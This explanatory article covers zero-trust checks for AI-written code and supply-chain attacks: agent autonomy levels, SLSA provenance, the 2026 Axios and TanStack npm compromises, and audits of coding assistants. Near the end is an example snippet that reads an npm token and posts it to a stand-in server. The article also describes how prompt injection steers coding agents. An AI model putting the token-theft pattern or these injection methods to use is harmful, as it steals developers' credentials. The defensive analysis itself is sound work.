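# Checking What AI-Generated Code Can Do Before It Runs: Zero-Trust Controls in the Software Supply Chain

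## AI-written code and the idea of trusting no code by default

Zero-trust controls for software decide, before a piece of code runs, whether what it can do is acceptable. A familiar publisher or a clean scan is not enough for code to pass. The term "zero trust" comes from network security, where it describes a way of handling users and devices. It has been extended to code in large part because of AI coding agents, which are language models set up to edit files, install packages and run commands to complete a programming task. An agent can write a program, fetch other people's software to go with it and run both within minutes, possibly before anyone has read any of the code.

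The controls apply throughout the software supply chain, which consists of the source code, third-party packages, build systems and registries used to produce a program and deliver it to users' machines. An artifact is any unit in that chain that someone can check and then run, such as a script, package, build output or container image (a program bundled with the files it needs).

Figures from Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, give a sense of how much of its code AI now writes. Anthropic's *When AI builds itself* reports that Claude wrote more than 80% of the code merged into the company's codebase as of May 2026, up from the low single digits before February 2025, when the company launched its coding agent, Claude Code, as a research preview. The prospectus for its share sale, Anthropic's *Amendment No. 1 to Form S-1 Registration Statement* (2026), gives the latest figure. Europa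 Press' *Claude ya escribe el 90 % del código de Anthropic* (2026) reports from that filing that Claude wrote more than 90% of code contributions in September 2026. "Contributions" may not mean quite the same thing as merged code, so the two percentages are only roughly comparable. The filing also puts the average daily volume of code per engineer in the third quarter at more than 45 times the 2024 average.

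Anthropic cautions that lines of code measure quantity, and that its own counts almost certainly overstate the gain in productivity. But the quantity is itself a problem for reviewers, who would have to read all those lines. The company expects human review to become the bottleneck if people cannot read code as fast as Claude writes it. Claude already reviews every proposed change at Anthropic before it merges. In a retrospective test, such a review would have caught roughly a third of the bugs behind past incidents on the company's chat service, which is useful but would still have let most of them through. Anthropic builds and sells coding agents, so it is hardly typical, and most other firms are probably some way behind it.

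### How an agent works, and the code it brings in

*Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (Jha, Anand and colleagues, 2026) reviews 142 studies on the security of "vibe coding", its term for development in which people describe what they want in ordinary language and AI does a growing share of the work. The systems it describes run in a loop. A developer types a request, such as for a page that exports invoices as PDF files. The host program, which is the editor or terminal tool around the model, adds relevant source files, error messages and sometimes notes from past sessions. It also adds instruction files such as AGENTS.md, which holds a project's standing directions for agents. The model receives all of this as one block of text. It then makes a plan and responds with code and with tool calls, which are requests to run a shell command, install a package or query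 a database.

The host carries out these requests, since the model cannot. The host also runs builds and tests and returns the output to the model, which revises its work and tries again. At more autonomous settings, the agent goes on after testing to open a pull request (a proposal to merge its changes), edit the pipeline that builds and releases the software, or deploy to production. The split between model and host matters for security because the host can refuse a tool call regardless of the model's reasons for making it.

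By the time the invoice page works, four kinds of code may have run on the developer's machine. The most visible is the code the agent wrote, which usually first runs when the agent tests it, often before a person has looked at the changes.

The agent will probably use an existing package to produce the PDF rather than write one. That package becomes a dependency, which is code, usually written by others, that a program loads and runs with the program's own access. Most languages don't isolate a library from the program that loads it, so if the invoice page can read the customer database, the PDF library can too. The package may well have dependencies of its own, which the agent didn't choose directly.

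Install scripts are code in a package that the package manager runs during installation. They have ordinary uses, such as compiling a component for the local machine. A check made after installation but before first use is too late to stop them.

Project configuration is easy to overlook because it looks like settings. Build files, test settings, Git hooks and editor task files can all specify commands that run when someone builds, tests, commits or, in some editors, opens the project. An agent can write such a file, and it can also trigger commands in a file someone else wrote just by running the repository's tests.

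The agent's settings determine how much of this a person sees. Jha and colleagues define six levels of autonomy by what the human still has to approve. At L2, the agent proposes edits across several files, and the developer accepts or rejects each set. At L3, it also runs commands and installs packages, so a flaw can affect the developer's machine or a build server. The developer approves individual commands, or perhaps only the risky ones. At L4, the developer sees the finished result, such as a pull request or a deployed application. At L5, the agent starts maintenance tasks by itself, and people approve only exceptions and the policies that govern it. The levels describe how an agent is used, so the same agent can work at L2 in one project and at L4 in another.

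### Three causes of harm

Code from any of these routes can do damage for three reasons, and a control that works against one may have no effect on another.

AI-written code can contain vulnerabilities by mistake, without any attacker involved. Jha and colleagues explain that models are geared toward code that runs and satisfies the literal request, while developers usually leave security requirements unstated. They cite an audit of 200 vibe-coded applications in which more than 90% had at least one vulnerability. That figure alone doesn't show how many of the flaws AI added. User studies provide more direct evidence of AI's effect on security, but their results differ on its size. In an experiment by Perry and colleagues, people who had an AI assistant wrote less secure code than people who worked without one, yet were more confident that it was safe. Another study, of programming in C,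 found a smaller effect. Neither study examined agents working alone.

Broken access control was the largest category of flaw in the audit, and any check on what code can reach can miss it. An invoice page that doesn't check whether the customer may open the invoice uses the same network and database access as a page that does. Other mistakes, such as a clean-up command that deletes the wrong directory, are more visible from outside the code.

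An agent can also go wrong because of text it reads. In prompt injection, someone plants text that the model then treats as an instruction. This is possible because the developer's request, retrieved files and tool output all enter the model as one sequence, with nothing that enforces a separation between instructions and data. The planted text can be in a README file, an issue report, a code comment or a package description, and an attacker can split it into fragments that look harmless individually. Filtering is difficult because software documentation is full of legitimate instructions to run commands, so a filter cannot reject everything that looks like an instruction. The planted text does not even have to contain an instruction. Jha and colleagues give the example of poisoned documentation for a login component, from which an agent copies a flawed way of checking tokens into the whole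 codebase, where it looks like an ordinary defect.

The remaining cause is a dependency that someone else has poisoned. The agent may have done exactly what the developer asked and chosen a sensible package, but the harm is in code that neither of them wrote. Jha and colleagues note that because agents often add packages automatically, a single upstream compromise can reach many projects without further effort from the attacker. The agent's own tooling is vulnerable in the same way. By October 30, 2026, Cursor, which makes an AI code editor, had said that a maliciously modified version of Anthropic's Claude Code extension was available, according to a photo caption published by Europa Press.

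The causes can overlap. Models sometimes mistakenly recommend packages that do not exist, and an attacker can then register the name and fill the package with malware. In all three cases, the code's origin may look legitimate. The careless page and the page shaped by an injected comment both come from the right agent, working under the right account in the right repository. A poisoned package can come from its usual publisher if an attacker has taken over that publisher's account.

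### Zero trust in networks

Network security faced a similar problem earlier. Companies used to defend a perimeter and treat whatever was inside it as safe, so an attacker who got through could move about freely. Rose, Borchert and colleagues (2020) set out the alternative for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) in *Zero Trust Architecture*, usually cited as SP 800-207. They trace the idea to a US defence programme called "black core" and to the Jericho Forum, which publicised the case against relying on a perimeter in 2004. They credit the name "zero trust" to John Kindervag, then at the research firm Forrester.

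The central rule of zero trust is that nobody is trusted solely because of where they are on the network or who owns their device. A zero-trust design assumes that an attacker is already present and that the company's own environment is no more trustworthy than any other. A company laptop in the office therefore goes through the same kind of check as a private phone in a café, even if the laptop has a good record. The system authenticates and authorises each request, and gives access only to those who need it. NIST's *Implementing a Zero Trust Architecture* (2022), a draft practice guide, lists what such a check looks at: the requester's identity and role, the health and credentials of the device, and the sensitivity of the resource.

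SP 800-207 divides access control between two components. According to NETSCOUT's *Interpreting NIST SP 800-207*, the policy decision point contains a policy engine that makes the final decision to grant or deny access. The policy enforcement point carries out that decision by opening, monitoring and ending connections between the requester and the resource, according to ColorTokens' *Zero Trust Architecture*. (Both companies sell security products.) This split keeps the rules in one place, and the enforcement point only has to apply the resulting decisions. It also makes the decision point a target, and Rose and colleagues list subversion of the decision process first among the threats. The same risk applies to coding agents, which often have write access to the files in which a project might keep its rules.

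Rose and colleagues include applications and other non-human entities among the "subjects" that request access in this scheme. But the check determines only whether an application may reach a given resource, such as a database, not whether the application should be running in the first place.

### Ammon's proposal to extend it to code

In *Ghosts in the machine*, an opinion piece for TechRadar, Ken Ammon proposed requiring permission for code to run, an approach he called "Zero Trust for Code". Ammon is chief executive of CodeHunter, which sells analysis of what software does, so he has a commercial interest in the conclusion. The piece reports no tests.

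Ammon first argues that most security workflows assume there is time to write, scan, test, approve and then deploy code, and to investigate afterwards if something looks wrong. When software goes from prompt to execution in minutes, that time is gone, and the code may have read secrets, opened connections or set itself up to keep running after a restart before anyone notices suspicious behaviour. AI also helps attackers by generating payload variants that match no known signature and have no reputation, good or bad. Ammon also writes that human reviewers are no longer in the loop, which is too strong as a general claim. It fits an agent at L4 or L5 fairly well, though even there people approve results or policies, but it does not fit an agent whose developer reads every edit.

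One of the proposal's two premises is that the origin of code does not show how it will behave. A buyer can learn an artifact's source and contents from its signatures, its provenance (a record of where it came from and how it was built) and its software bill of materials, or SBOM (a list of its components). Code can pass all of those checks and still break a rule when it runs. In Ammon's example, an AI-generated script completes its task but exposes data in the process, without anyone intending harm.

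The other premise is that malicious code must act on its environment. An attacker can keep rewriting a payload, but a payload that steals credentials has to read them and send them somewhere, and one that encrypts a disk has to write to it. Ammon therefore considers the code's capabilities a more durable signal than its appearance.

From these premises Ammon concludes that someone should check software's expected behaviour against policy before it runs, then allow, block, restrict or isolate it, or pass it to a person. Existing controls would stay in place and provide useful but inconclusive evidence. An organisation would begin by mapping every path by which code enters and runs, including repositories, packages, containers, build pipelines, email attachments, macros, browser extensions and scripts from AI tools. It would then find the paths where code runs only because it came from an approved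 source or has no bad history.

The parallel with networks is inexact. A system can look up a user's role and a device's credentials when a request arrives, but it has to predict what a program will do, so the check depends heavily on how accurate the prediction is.

### Capability and intent

A capability, in this setting, is a kind of access that code is able to use, such as the network, files, subprocesses (other programs that it starts) or environment variables (named values that the operating system passes to a program, passwords and access tokens often among them). Consider one line of Python:

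```python
subprocess.run(command, shell=True)
```

The line passes the text in `command` to the system's shell, which runs it as a new process with the same user's rights and, by default, the same environment variables. In the build script of a PDF library, `command` might call a C compiler to build a component that draws fonts. In an attacker's install script, the same call might collect cloud credentials from the environment and send them to a server abroad. Because a shell can reach the network and the file system, granting this capability in practice grants most of the others.

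The capability-intent gap is the difference between what a call makes possible and the purpose it serves, which the call itself does not show. Reading the value of `command` narrows the gap considerably if the value is written in the code rather than assembled at run time or downloaded. Even a readable command can leave the purpose unclear. To spare users a slow compilation, a legitimate package may download a prebuilt binary from a server and run it, and a malicious package may also download and run a binary. Telling them apart requires knowing whose server it is and what the binary does.

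If malicious code has to act on its environment, as it does under the second premise, its actions are in principle observable when it performs them. Their purpose may still be a matter of interpretation, as with the downloaded binary, so the premise does not fully support Ammon's claim that the behaviour of malware "cannot conceal its intent".

A policy can avoid part of the difficulty by limiting code to the access it needs. A library that formats invoices doesn't need to contact the internet, and a rule that denies it network access works the same way against a thief, a misled agent and a careless programmer. Such rules can be applied without knowing anyone's intent, though they have drawbacks, mainly for harmless packages that do need broad access.

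### The path through a gate

A gate is the point where an artifact waits while a system applies the policy to it. The gate's decision, called the verdict, is to allow the artifact, allow it with limits, hold it for review, or block it. Ammon's "restrict" and "isolate" are both ways of allowing with limits. Suppose the agent with the invoice page asks to install a PDF library.

The gate first has to identify the artifact by its cryptographic hash, a short value computed from the file's entire contents, because two different files can have the same name and version number. It also needs a list of the other packages and any install scripts that the library would bring in, and a description of the environment where the code will run, because a developer's laptop full of credentials requires different rules from an empty test machine.

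The gate then gathers evidence. Provenance records can show who built the package and from which source. Static scanning searches the code for signs of flaws or malice without running it, and capability analysis works out what kinds of access the code could use. A trial run executes the package in an isolated environment and records what it does there. If the project already uses an older version believed to be good, the gate can compare the new version against it.

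The policy is a set of written rules for making a decision based on the findings. One rule might let document libraries read and write inside the project folder and do nothing else. A PDF library that follows this rule passes. If its install script needs a compiler, the gate might allow the installation without network access or credentials in the environment. The gate would hold a new version for human review if it contacts a host the old one never used, and would block a version that reads cloud credentials and sends them out.

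Enforcement has to happen somewhere the agent cannot change, such as the host program, the package manager's connection to the registry or the operating system. The agent's loop makes this harder because it returns a refusal to the model as an error to fix. The model may then try to download the same package by another route or copy its source into the project, and an enforcement point that covers only the usual install command would miss both. The gate's verdict applies only to the exact bytes it examined, so a file that changes afterwards has to go through the gate again.

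## What provenance and signatures prove

Provenance is often the easiest evidence for a gate to use, since the publisher's build system has already produced it and checking it takes little time. It usually comes as an attestation, a signed statement about an artifact. npm, the main registry for JavaScript packages, distributes attestations with the packages. Attestations can show quite reliably where a package came from. How much that helps against an attacker depends on where the attacker got in, as two attacks on npm packages in 2026 illustrate.

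### From a commit to a signed package

Suppose the maintainers of the PDF library in the invoice example release a new version. They start from a commit, a saved state of the source code. Git identifies each commit by a hash of its contents and history, so changing the code later would change the identifier.

A hosted build service, such as GitHub Actions, starts a temporary machine, fetches a commit and follows the instructions in a workflow file from the repository. According to GitHub's *Introducing npm package provenance* (2023), npm's provenance requires a trusted build platform because this shows which commit triggered the build and which instructions were used to publish the result. A maintainer who builds and uploads the package from a laptop can't get provenance this way.

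The build job now needs to prove which project it belongs to. The build service gives it a token, in the standard OpenID Connect (OIDC) format, that identifies the job's repository and workflow. The job sends the token to Sigstore, a project that runs a public certificate authority. Sigstore checks the token and issues a short-lived certificate that ties a signing key to the job's identity. Maintainers therefore have no long-lived signing key that someone could steal, but an attacker who steals the token while the job is running can sign as the project.

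The job uses the key to sign the attestation. The usual format comes from in-toto, a framework for recording the steps by which software is made. It pairs a subject, which is the artifact's name and hash, with a set of claims about that subject. Simplified and with invented values, the provenance of the PDF library might look like this:

```json
{
  "subject": { "name": "example-pdf 2.4.1", "sha512": "9f2c..." },
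  "claims": {
    "repository": "example-org/example-pdf",
    "commit": "71ab...",
    "workflow": "release.yml on branch main",
    "builder": "GitHub-hosted runner"
  }
}
```

A record of the signing also goes into a public log. npm's *Generating provenance statements* describes the log as tamper-evident and explains that it would help people notice altered packages if an attacker compromised the registry.

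The consumer, which may be a developer, a company's package proxy or the host program around an agent, then has to check the attestation. It computes the hash of the downloaded file, compares it with the one in the attestation, and verifies the signature and certificate. These checks establish that some build on a recognised service produced exactly this file. The consumer also has to compare the repository, workflow and builder with the ones it expects for this package, because otherwise an attestation from an attacker's own repository would pass. The expected values have to come from outside the attestation, such as from earlier releases or a list that the company maintains.

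npm warns that provenance does not guarantee that a package contains no malicious code. Provenance provides a verifiable link to the source code and build instructions, which someone still has to examine even after a complete check.

The same OIDC token can also be used for trusted publishing. npm can accept it as permission to upload a package, so the project no longer needs a long-lived npm token. In the two 2026 attacks, one attacker bypassed trusted publishing and the other used it from the inside.

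### The SLSA levels

The harder it is to obtain a false provenance record, the more a provenance record can be trusted. Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts (SLSA), an industry specification, grades this difficulty. Its Build track defines three levels above zero.

At Build L1, the package comes with a record of who built it, how, and from what main inputs. The record can be incomplete or unsigned, so forging it is trivial. It is mainly useful for catching mistakes, such as a release built from a commit that isn't in the public repository.

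Build L2 requires a hosted platform that generates and signs the provenance itself, and a consumer who checks that the provenance is authentic. The signature protects against tampering after the build, because a swapped file no longer matches the signed hash. Forging the provenance at this level requires a deliberate attack, though according to the specification that attack may be easy.

Build L3 adds protection during the build. The platform has to prevent one run from influencing another, even within the same project, and keep signing secrets out of reach of the build steps that the project's developers write. To forge provenance, an attacker would have to exploit a vulnerability that most adversaries lack the ability to exploit. The specification recommends L3 for most software releases but says existing platforms usually need significant changes to reach it.

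A SLSA level applies to only one build, so a package built at L3 can load dependencies with no provenance. A draft of version 1.1 of the SLSA specification explains that requiring the same level throughout the supply chain would force everyone to start at the far end and wait for each link in turn. The rule is practical, but an agent that installs one well-attested package may also bring in dozens of others that the attestation doesn't cover.

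The Build levels also take the source code as given. Version 1.2 added a separate Source Track, which covers how each change got into the repository. SLSA's *Source* sets out four levels. L1 requires version control. L2 requires a history that nobody can rewrite and source provenance, which records who made each change, when, and which controls applied. At L3, the repository host continuously enforces the organisation's own rules on protected branches, such as requiring tests to pass before a merge. At L4, two trusted people must approve every change, including any revisions made during review.

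The specification defines a trusted person as a human, so if an agent submits a change under its own account, two people have to review it to satisfy L4. If a developer submits the agent's code under their own account, they count as one of the two, whether or not they have read it. Organisations may also give a "trusted robot" a standing exception from review. The specification's examples are bots that move code between repositories and Dependabot, which proposes dependency updates. A robot qualifies only if nobody can unilaterally influence its identity and codebase. A coding agent could meet that condition as written and still follow instructions in a bug report comment, because prompt injection changes what an agent does without changing its codebase.

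### What an SBOM lists

A software bill of materials (SBOM) provides narrower information than provenance does. The SLSA draft compares an SBOM to the ingredient label on food, and SLSA to the hygiene rules and tamper-proof seals that make the label credible. When someone discloses a flaw in a library, a company with good SBOMs can quickly find which of its products contain that library. *Do AI Coding Assistants Check Before They Install?* (Shan, 2026) notes that the EU's Cyber Resilience Act now requires a machine-readable SBOM for the products it covers.

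An SBOM for the invoice page would list the PDF library and the packages that came with it. It would not show whether any of them contacts the internet or reads files outside the project, or whether the page's own code lacks an access check. Comparing two SBOMs can still help, because a component that first appears in a minor update is worth checking.

### Axios, where provenance was missing

On March 31, 2026, an attacker took over the npm account of a maintainer of Axios, a JavaScript library for making web requests. Datadog Security Labs' *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (2026) counts 174,000 npm packages that depend on Axios. The attacker published two malicious versions, 1.14.1 and 0.30.4, which stayed available for roughly three hours.

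The source code of axios 1.14.1 was identical to that of the previous version, 1.14.0. The attacker had added a dependency, `plain-crypto-js`, whose name resembles that of a well-known package, `crypto-js`. Axios never used it, but npm installs dependencies automatically, and this one had an install script that downloaded a remote-access trojan, a program that lets an attacker control the machine. The script then replaced the package's description with a clean copy, so anyone who inspected the folder afterwards would have found no sign of an install script.

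npm's public records show how the two releases differed. Datadog Security Labs found that GitHub Actions had published 1.14.0 through trusted publishing, while 1.14.1 came directly from the maintainer's account, which by then had a new email address. The malicious versions had no provenance, VentureBeat reported. SafeDep's *axios Compromised* likewise describes an attack that bypassed the project's build pipeline and its provenance attestations entirely.

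Accounts differ on which credential the attacker used. In a post-mortem quoted on an Openwall mailing list (2026), the maintainer wrote that the attacker used social engineering and malware to get into the maintainer's PC and steal the npm account credentials. UNU (the United Nations University), citing the security firm Huntress, attributes the upload to a long-lived access token that the project still kept alongside trusted publishing. In either case, the stolen credential let the attacker upload a package without touching the official build.

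The malicious versions of Axios had no provenance, though trade coverage has reported otherwise. ReversingLabs, which sells software analysis, quotes Denis Calderone of Suzu Labs as saying, "The provenance was legitimate." Calderone also called the SBOM clean, but an accurate SBOM for version 1.14.1 would have listed `plain-crypto-js`, a package less than a day old. A gate that accepted Axios only with provenance from the project's own repository would have rejected both malicious versions, but as VentureBeat points out, no gate was rejecting packages for lacking it. The error about provenance matters because it makes the attack look like evidence that checking provenance is useless.

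Requiring provenance for every package would have stopped both 1.14.1 and 0.30.4, but presumably also legitimate 0.x releases and every other package without provenance. The maintainer said that trusted publishing covered only the 1.x line, and that the older 0.x line still relied on a long-lived token. A gate that raised an alarm only when a package lost provenance it used to have would therefore have caught 1.14.1 but might well have let 0.30.4 through.

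Even if the rule had blocked this attack, the attacker might have found a way around it. The attacker also controlled the maintainer's GitHub account and used it to delete two reports of the compromise. Someone with that access might have been able to commit the new dependency and let the official workflow publish it with genuine provenance, though this would have been slower and more visible. Mandatory review by a second person, as in Source L4, addresses this route, but the hijacked account had higher permissions than the maintainer who first responded, perhaps enough to turn off the review requirement.

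### TanStack, where provenance was valid

Six weeks later, another attacker did get genuine provenance. On May 11, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-45321* (2026), the attacker took about six minutes to publish 84 malicious versions of 42 packages from TanStack, a family of JavaScript libraries for building web applications. The malware stole cloud credentials, GitHub tokens and SSH keys, and tried to spread by republishing other packages that its victims maintained. Grafana Labs, which makes monitoring software, was among the companies it reached.

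InfoQ's *TanStack Details Sophisticated npm Supply Chain Attack That Compromised 42 Packages* (2026) recounts the attack from the project's post-mortem. The attacker proposed a harmless-looking change from a copy of the repository. One of TanStack's workflows ran code from such proposals with the project's permissions, and the attacker's code used those permissions to plant files in a cache that other builds shared. The maintainers later merged unrelated changes, which started the release workflow. The workflow loaded the poisoned cache and ran the attacker's code inside the official build, where the code took the job's OIDC token and published the packages. The attacker did not steal an npm token or alter the release workflow.

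The attestations named the right repository, workflow and branch, because the build had taken place there. A gate that checked all three against expected values would have let the packages in.

Several reports went further and described the provenance as SLSA Build Level 3. Infosecurity Magazine's *Mini Shai-Hulud Hits TanStack npm Packages* attributes this to the security firm StepSecurity, which drew the lesson that provenance confirms which pipeline produced an artifact, not whether the pipeline was behaving as intended. The lesson is sound, but the SLSA project disputes the level. In its reply, it agrees that the signatures were valid and argues that the platform behind them met only L2, which is what npm's built-in provenance achieves. L3 forbids three things that happened here:

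- one build put false entries into a cache that another build used
- build steps got access to the identity used for signing
- one build influenced the environment of a later one

The project concludes that a platform that met L3 would have prevented the cache poisoning. This follows fairly directly from the wording of the standard, although the project has an obvious interest in defending the standard and reports no test. L3 also depends on someone's honesty. On GitHub, developers currently reach L3 by calling a shared workflow that they don't write themselves, which shifts trust from individual developers to whoever controls that workflow.

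The SLSA project acknowledges limits to its standard. Provenance records what happened in a build, and the consumer has to judge whether that was good enough. Once an attacker's code runs inside a trusted workflow, no policy applied to the resulting attestation can undo the compromise. SLSA also does not assess whether a workflow's triggers and permissions are safe, so the setting that let the TanStack attacker in was outside its scope. The Source Track would probably not have helped either, because it covers code that people merge into protected branches, and the malicious code took effect without a merge.

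Other signed attestations can cover vulnerability scans, code reviews and component lists, and in principle how a package behaved in a trial run. Few organisations have the resources to verify all of these for every dependency, so SLSA allows a trusted verifier to check them once and publish a signed summary that consumers can rely on.

The malicious releases did differ from normal ones in one way: both workflow runs that published them failed, because the malware broke the project's tests. The SLSA project suggests an alert for any package published by a failed run, which it says would have detected the attack within minutes. The alert seems worth having, but it would have worked here only because the attacker made a mistake. Outside researchers noticed the packages in about 20 minutes anyway, and InfoQ reports that TanStack acknowledged the compromise could have stayed hidden far longer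 if the tests had kept passing.

### Independent rebuilding

Rebuilding is a way to check the build without trusting the machine that performed it. An independent party takes the same source, builds it on its own infrastructure and publishes the result in its own repository. In the TanStack case, a rebuilder would not have shared the poisoned cache, so a company that installed the rebuilder's copy would have received packages without the malware.

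The rebuilder can also compare its package with the official one. If the build is reproducible, meaning that the same source and tools always produce the same bytes, any difference needs an explanation. Many builds aren't reproducible, often for harmless reasons such as a timestamp inside the file. A mismatch in those builds proves little, but installing the rebuilt copy still avoids the original pipeline.

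Older attacks show where rebuilding helps. The SLSA draft's table of past incidents includes event-stream, in which an attacker published a malicious package version without a matching change to the source. A rebuild from the public source would not have contained the malicious code. The table also includes SushiSwap, where a contractor with repository access committed code that redirected cryptocurrency to the contractor. A rebuild would have reproduced that code, and the draft's remedy for that attack is review by two people.

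A rebuilder can also miss an attack that comes through its inputs. If it downloads the same poisoned dependency during the build, it may produce the same poisoned package, and the match would look reassuring. Rebuilding also takes time, so a gate that relies on it has to wait before accepting new releases.

### Agents' commits and invented package names

Axios and TanStack were attacks on third-party packages. For code that an agent writes itself, signatures prove even less about safety, because there is usually no impersonation to detect. The invoice page with the missing access check would have a valid signature from the right account and provenance that correctly links the deployed program to its commit.

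The signature is of some use if the agent has its own account, because reviewers can tell its commits from a developer's, send them for extra review, and find them all if the agent turns out to have been misled. The signature doesn't make this possible if the agent works under the developer's account. An agent with permission to edit workflow files can also introduce an unsafe setting like TanStack's, and the project's later releases would still receive valid attestations.

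Provenance has a different weakness when an agent installs a package whose name a model invented and an attacker then registered. Shan credits work by Spracklen and colleagues, presented at USENIX Security 2025, with showing that code-generating models systematically invent package names and that attackers can exploit this.

An attacker can give a package of this kind genuine provenance by creating a public repository, writing an ordinary workflow and letting GitHub build and sign the result. With a suitable platform, the package could even reach Build L3. Provenance protects well against impostors of a known package, because they can't produce an attestation from the real project's repository. An invented name has no real project behind it, so the consumer has nothing to compare the attestation with. Lookalike names leave a similar gap. The SLSA draft says that SLSA does not directly address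 them, but that the link to a source repository can support other defences. For instance, a gate could follow the link and find that the repository is two days old and has a single contributor.

### Whether coding assistants check

This evidence is useful only if something reads it before the installation runs. In an audit published in September 2026, Shan tested whether AI coding assistants read such evidence before installing third-party research software. The audit did not cover code the assistants had written. Shan fixed and deposited the protocol before running any trials.

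The six projects were drawn at random from supercomputing and quantum computing projects that met set criteria. Shan made nine modified copies of each. One was a control with nothing added. Four each had one valid signal: an SBOM, a signed release, a build attestation, or a file declaring the project's official channels. Two had a signature or attestation from the wrong issuer, as a hijacked release might. One had all four valid signals, and the last had contradictions in the project's own metadata.

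In each trial, an assistant received one copy in an isolated container and had to install it. In half the trials, a host program asked for approval before every command and a script granted every request. The other half ran without approvals. Shan scored the trials from the container's logs of files opened and commands run, and ignored what the assistants claimed to have done.

In 9 of the main study's 1,920 trials (0.5%), assistants opened one of the signals before deciding whether to install. They never ran a command to verify one. A smaller supplement with three more capable models had much the same result.

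| Model | Trials | Opened a signal before deciding | Ran a verification command | Cost per trial |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder 14B (run locally) | 1,200 | 0 | 0 | $0.00 |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite | 360 | 0 | 0 | $0.01 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 360 | 9 | 0 | $0.10 |
| Kimi K2.6 (supplement) | 72 | 1 | 0 | $0.05 |
| GPT-5.6 (supplement) | 72 | 0 | 0 | $0.07 |
| Claude Fable 5 (supplement) | 50 | 0 | 0 | $1.00 |

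Adding signals made no measurable difference. Assistants opened a signal in 8 of 1,344 trials where signals were present and in none of 384 control trials (p = 0.50 in the planned test). Forged material got no more attention than valid material, because no assistant reached the step where the two would look different. Asking for approval did not help either, with 3 positive trials out of 960 compared with 6 out of 960 without it. The approvals came from a script that always agreed, which is a poor substitute for a careful person but may be a fair one for someone who clicks "approve" out of habit.

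The low rate is well supported for these conditions, but the comparisons between models are not. With 50 trials, Fable's true rate could be as high as 7%. The local model finished in about two steps on average, so it hardly examined the projects.

The set-up may also have discouraged checking. The containers had little beyond basic build tools and no network access, so the assistants could not consult Sigstore's public log. The assistants installed from a local folder, whereas an agent would normally fetch a PDF library by name from a registry. Shan used one fixed prompt per host program, so the audit does not show what assistants do when told to verify first. The trials ran between August 30 and September 3, and later models may behave differently.

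Related work suggests that the problem extends beyond research software. In a July 2026 study summarised by Shan, Bagmar and Saraf tested whether coding agents notice attacks when installing mainstream packages. Across 4 host programs, 7 models and 12 attack scenarios, no combination detected a vulnerable version. Detection in general depended on the combination of host program and model.

Publishers also need to provide signatures and provenance. In an earlier check of 30 supercomputing and quantum-computing projects, Shan found that two published signed releases, one had an attestation and none had an SBOM. A gate that required provenance from such projects would block nearly all of them.

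Shan concludes that the host program should verify signatures and attestations before every installation and log the result, whichever model it runs. The host is well placed to do this because it can refuse a command regardless of what the model has read. The audit did not include a host program with such a step, so how well it would work in practice is still unknown.

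## What static scanning finds and misses

Provenance checks don't examine a package's contents, so a gate also has to check the code. Static scanning is usually the fastest way to do this and may take only a few seconds. In the Axios attack, a scanner could have examined the install script before npm ran it and the script downloaded the trojan.

Vulnerability scanners look for flaws an attacker could use, such as a database query that includes unchecked user input. Malware scanners look for code written to do harm. Passing one kind of scan is weak evidence that code would pass the other. The invoice page with the missing access check isn't malware, and a program that steals passwords may have no vulnerabilities.

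Vulnerabilities are often easier to define than malware. Whether user input reaches a query unchecked is a fact about the code, while malice depends on the code's purpose, so malware scanners have to deal with the capability-intent gap. The evidence also covers different code, since Veracode tested AI-written code for vulnerabilities, while the studies of malware detectors used third-party packages from npm and PyPI, the main Python registry.

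### Vulnerabilities in AI-written code

Veracode, which sells a vulnerability scanner, regularly tests how often language models write insecure code. Its *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* gives an average security pass rate of 56%, compared with 55% in the first report. About 44% of the tasks therefore produced code with a known type of flaw, though nearly all the code was syntactically valid. GPT-5.5 had the highest pass rate of the 11 models in the latest round, at 68%, and more than half of the models scored between 50% and 53%.

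Veracode's *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) describes a test of 80 coding tasks, five for each combination of four programming languages and four types of flaw. In each task, the model must complete a function from a comment describing what it should do. Every task has both a secure and an insecure working solution. Veracode then runs its own static scanner on the result. Pass rates varied greatly between the types of flaw.

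| Flaw | What an attacker could do | Pass rate |
|---|---|---|
| Insecure cryptography | Break encryption that relies on a weak algorithm | 87% |
| SQL injection | Alter a database query by typing part of one into a form | 83% |
| Cross-site scripting | Make a web page run a script in another user's browser | 15% |
| Log injection | Add false entries to a program's log | 12% |

(The four rates average 49%, so the overall 56% presumably comes from a different mix of tasks or models.)

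Veracode's explanation is that models have learned to avoid flaws with a recognisable pattern, but have trouble following user input through several lines or files. That may be right, but the figures also include the scanner's mistakes, and a single function may not show whether the rest of the program cleans the input first. Some of the failures in the bottom two rows could therefore be false positives, meaning harmless code flagged as harmful.

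The 44% comes from tasks that each contained an opportunity to make one of four mistakes, and much ordinary code contains no such opportunity. It is therefore not the share of all AI-written code that has a flaw, although Veracode's publicity comes close to presenting it that way. The test also leaves out broken access control, the largest category in the audit of vibe-coded applications. It has no results from human programmers on the same tasks, so it can't show whether AI-written code is worse than theirs.

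Veracode's *LLMs Are Getting Smarter, But Not Safer* (2026) also did not test agents. The models worked without tools, guardrails or human review, and the prompts did not mention security. An agent that scans its own code and fixes what it finds might do much better. Models that reason before answering did somewhat better than the others, at 56% against 51%. Veracode suggests this is because the reasoning works as a kind of internal review.

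Veracode counted only flaws that a static scanner found, so running such a scanner on an agent's code would catch these mistakes. This seems well worth doing for code that handles user input. A scanner is much less likely to detect that the invoice page should have checked who owns the invoice, because nothing in the code states that rule.

### Four ways to look for malice

Suppose the PDF library from the invoice example contains these lines of JavaScript:

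```javascript
const https = require("https");
const token = process.env.NPM_TOKEN;
const body = JSON.stringify({ token });
https.request("https://stats.example", { method: "POST" }).end(body);
```

The second line reads a token for publishing npm packages from the environment variables. The third turns it into text, and the fourth sends that text to an outside server.

The simplest method uses pattern rules, which match particular words or code structures. A rule might flag any use of `process.env` or `https.request`. It would catch this code, along with every harmless package that reads a setting or contacts a server. Some rules also match text in documentation. OSSGadget, a Microsoft tool, flags packages because the download commands `curl` and `wget` appear in a README file. Capability analysis lists the sensitive calls in a package without treating them as signs of malice, which can still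 be useful.

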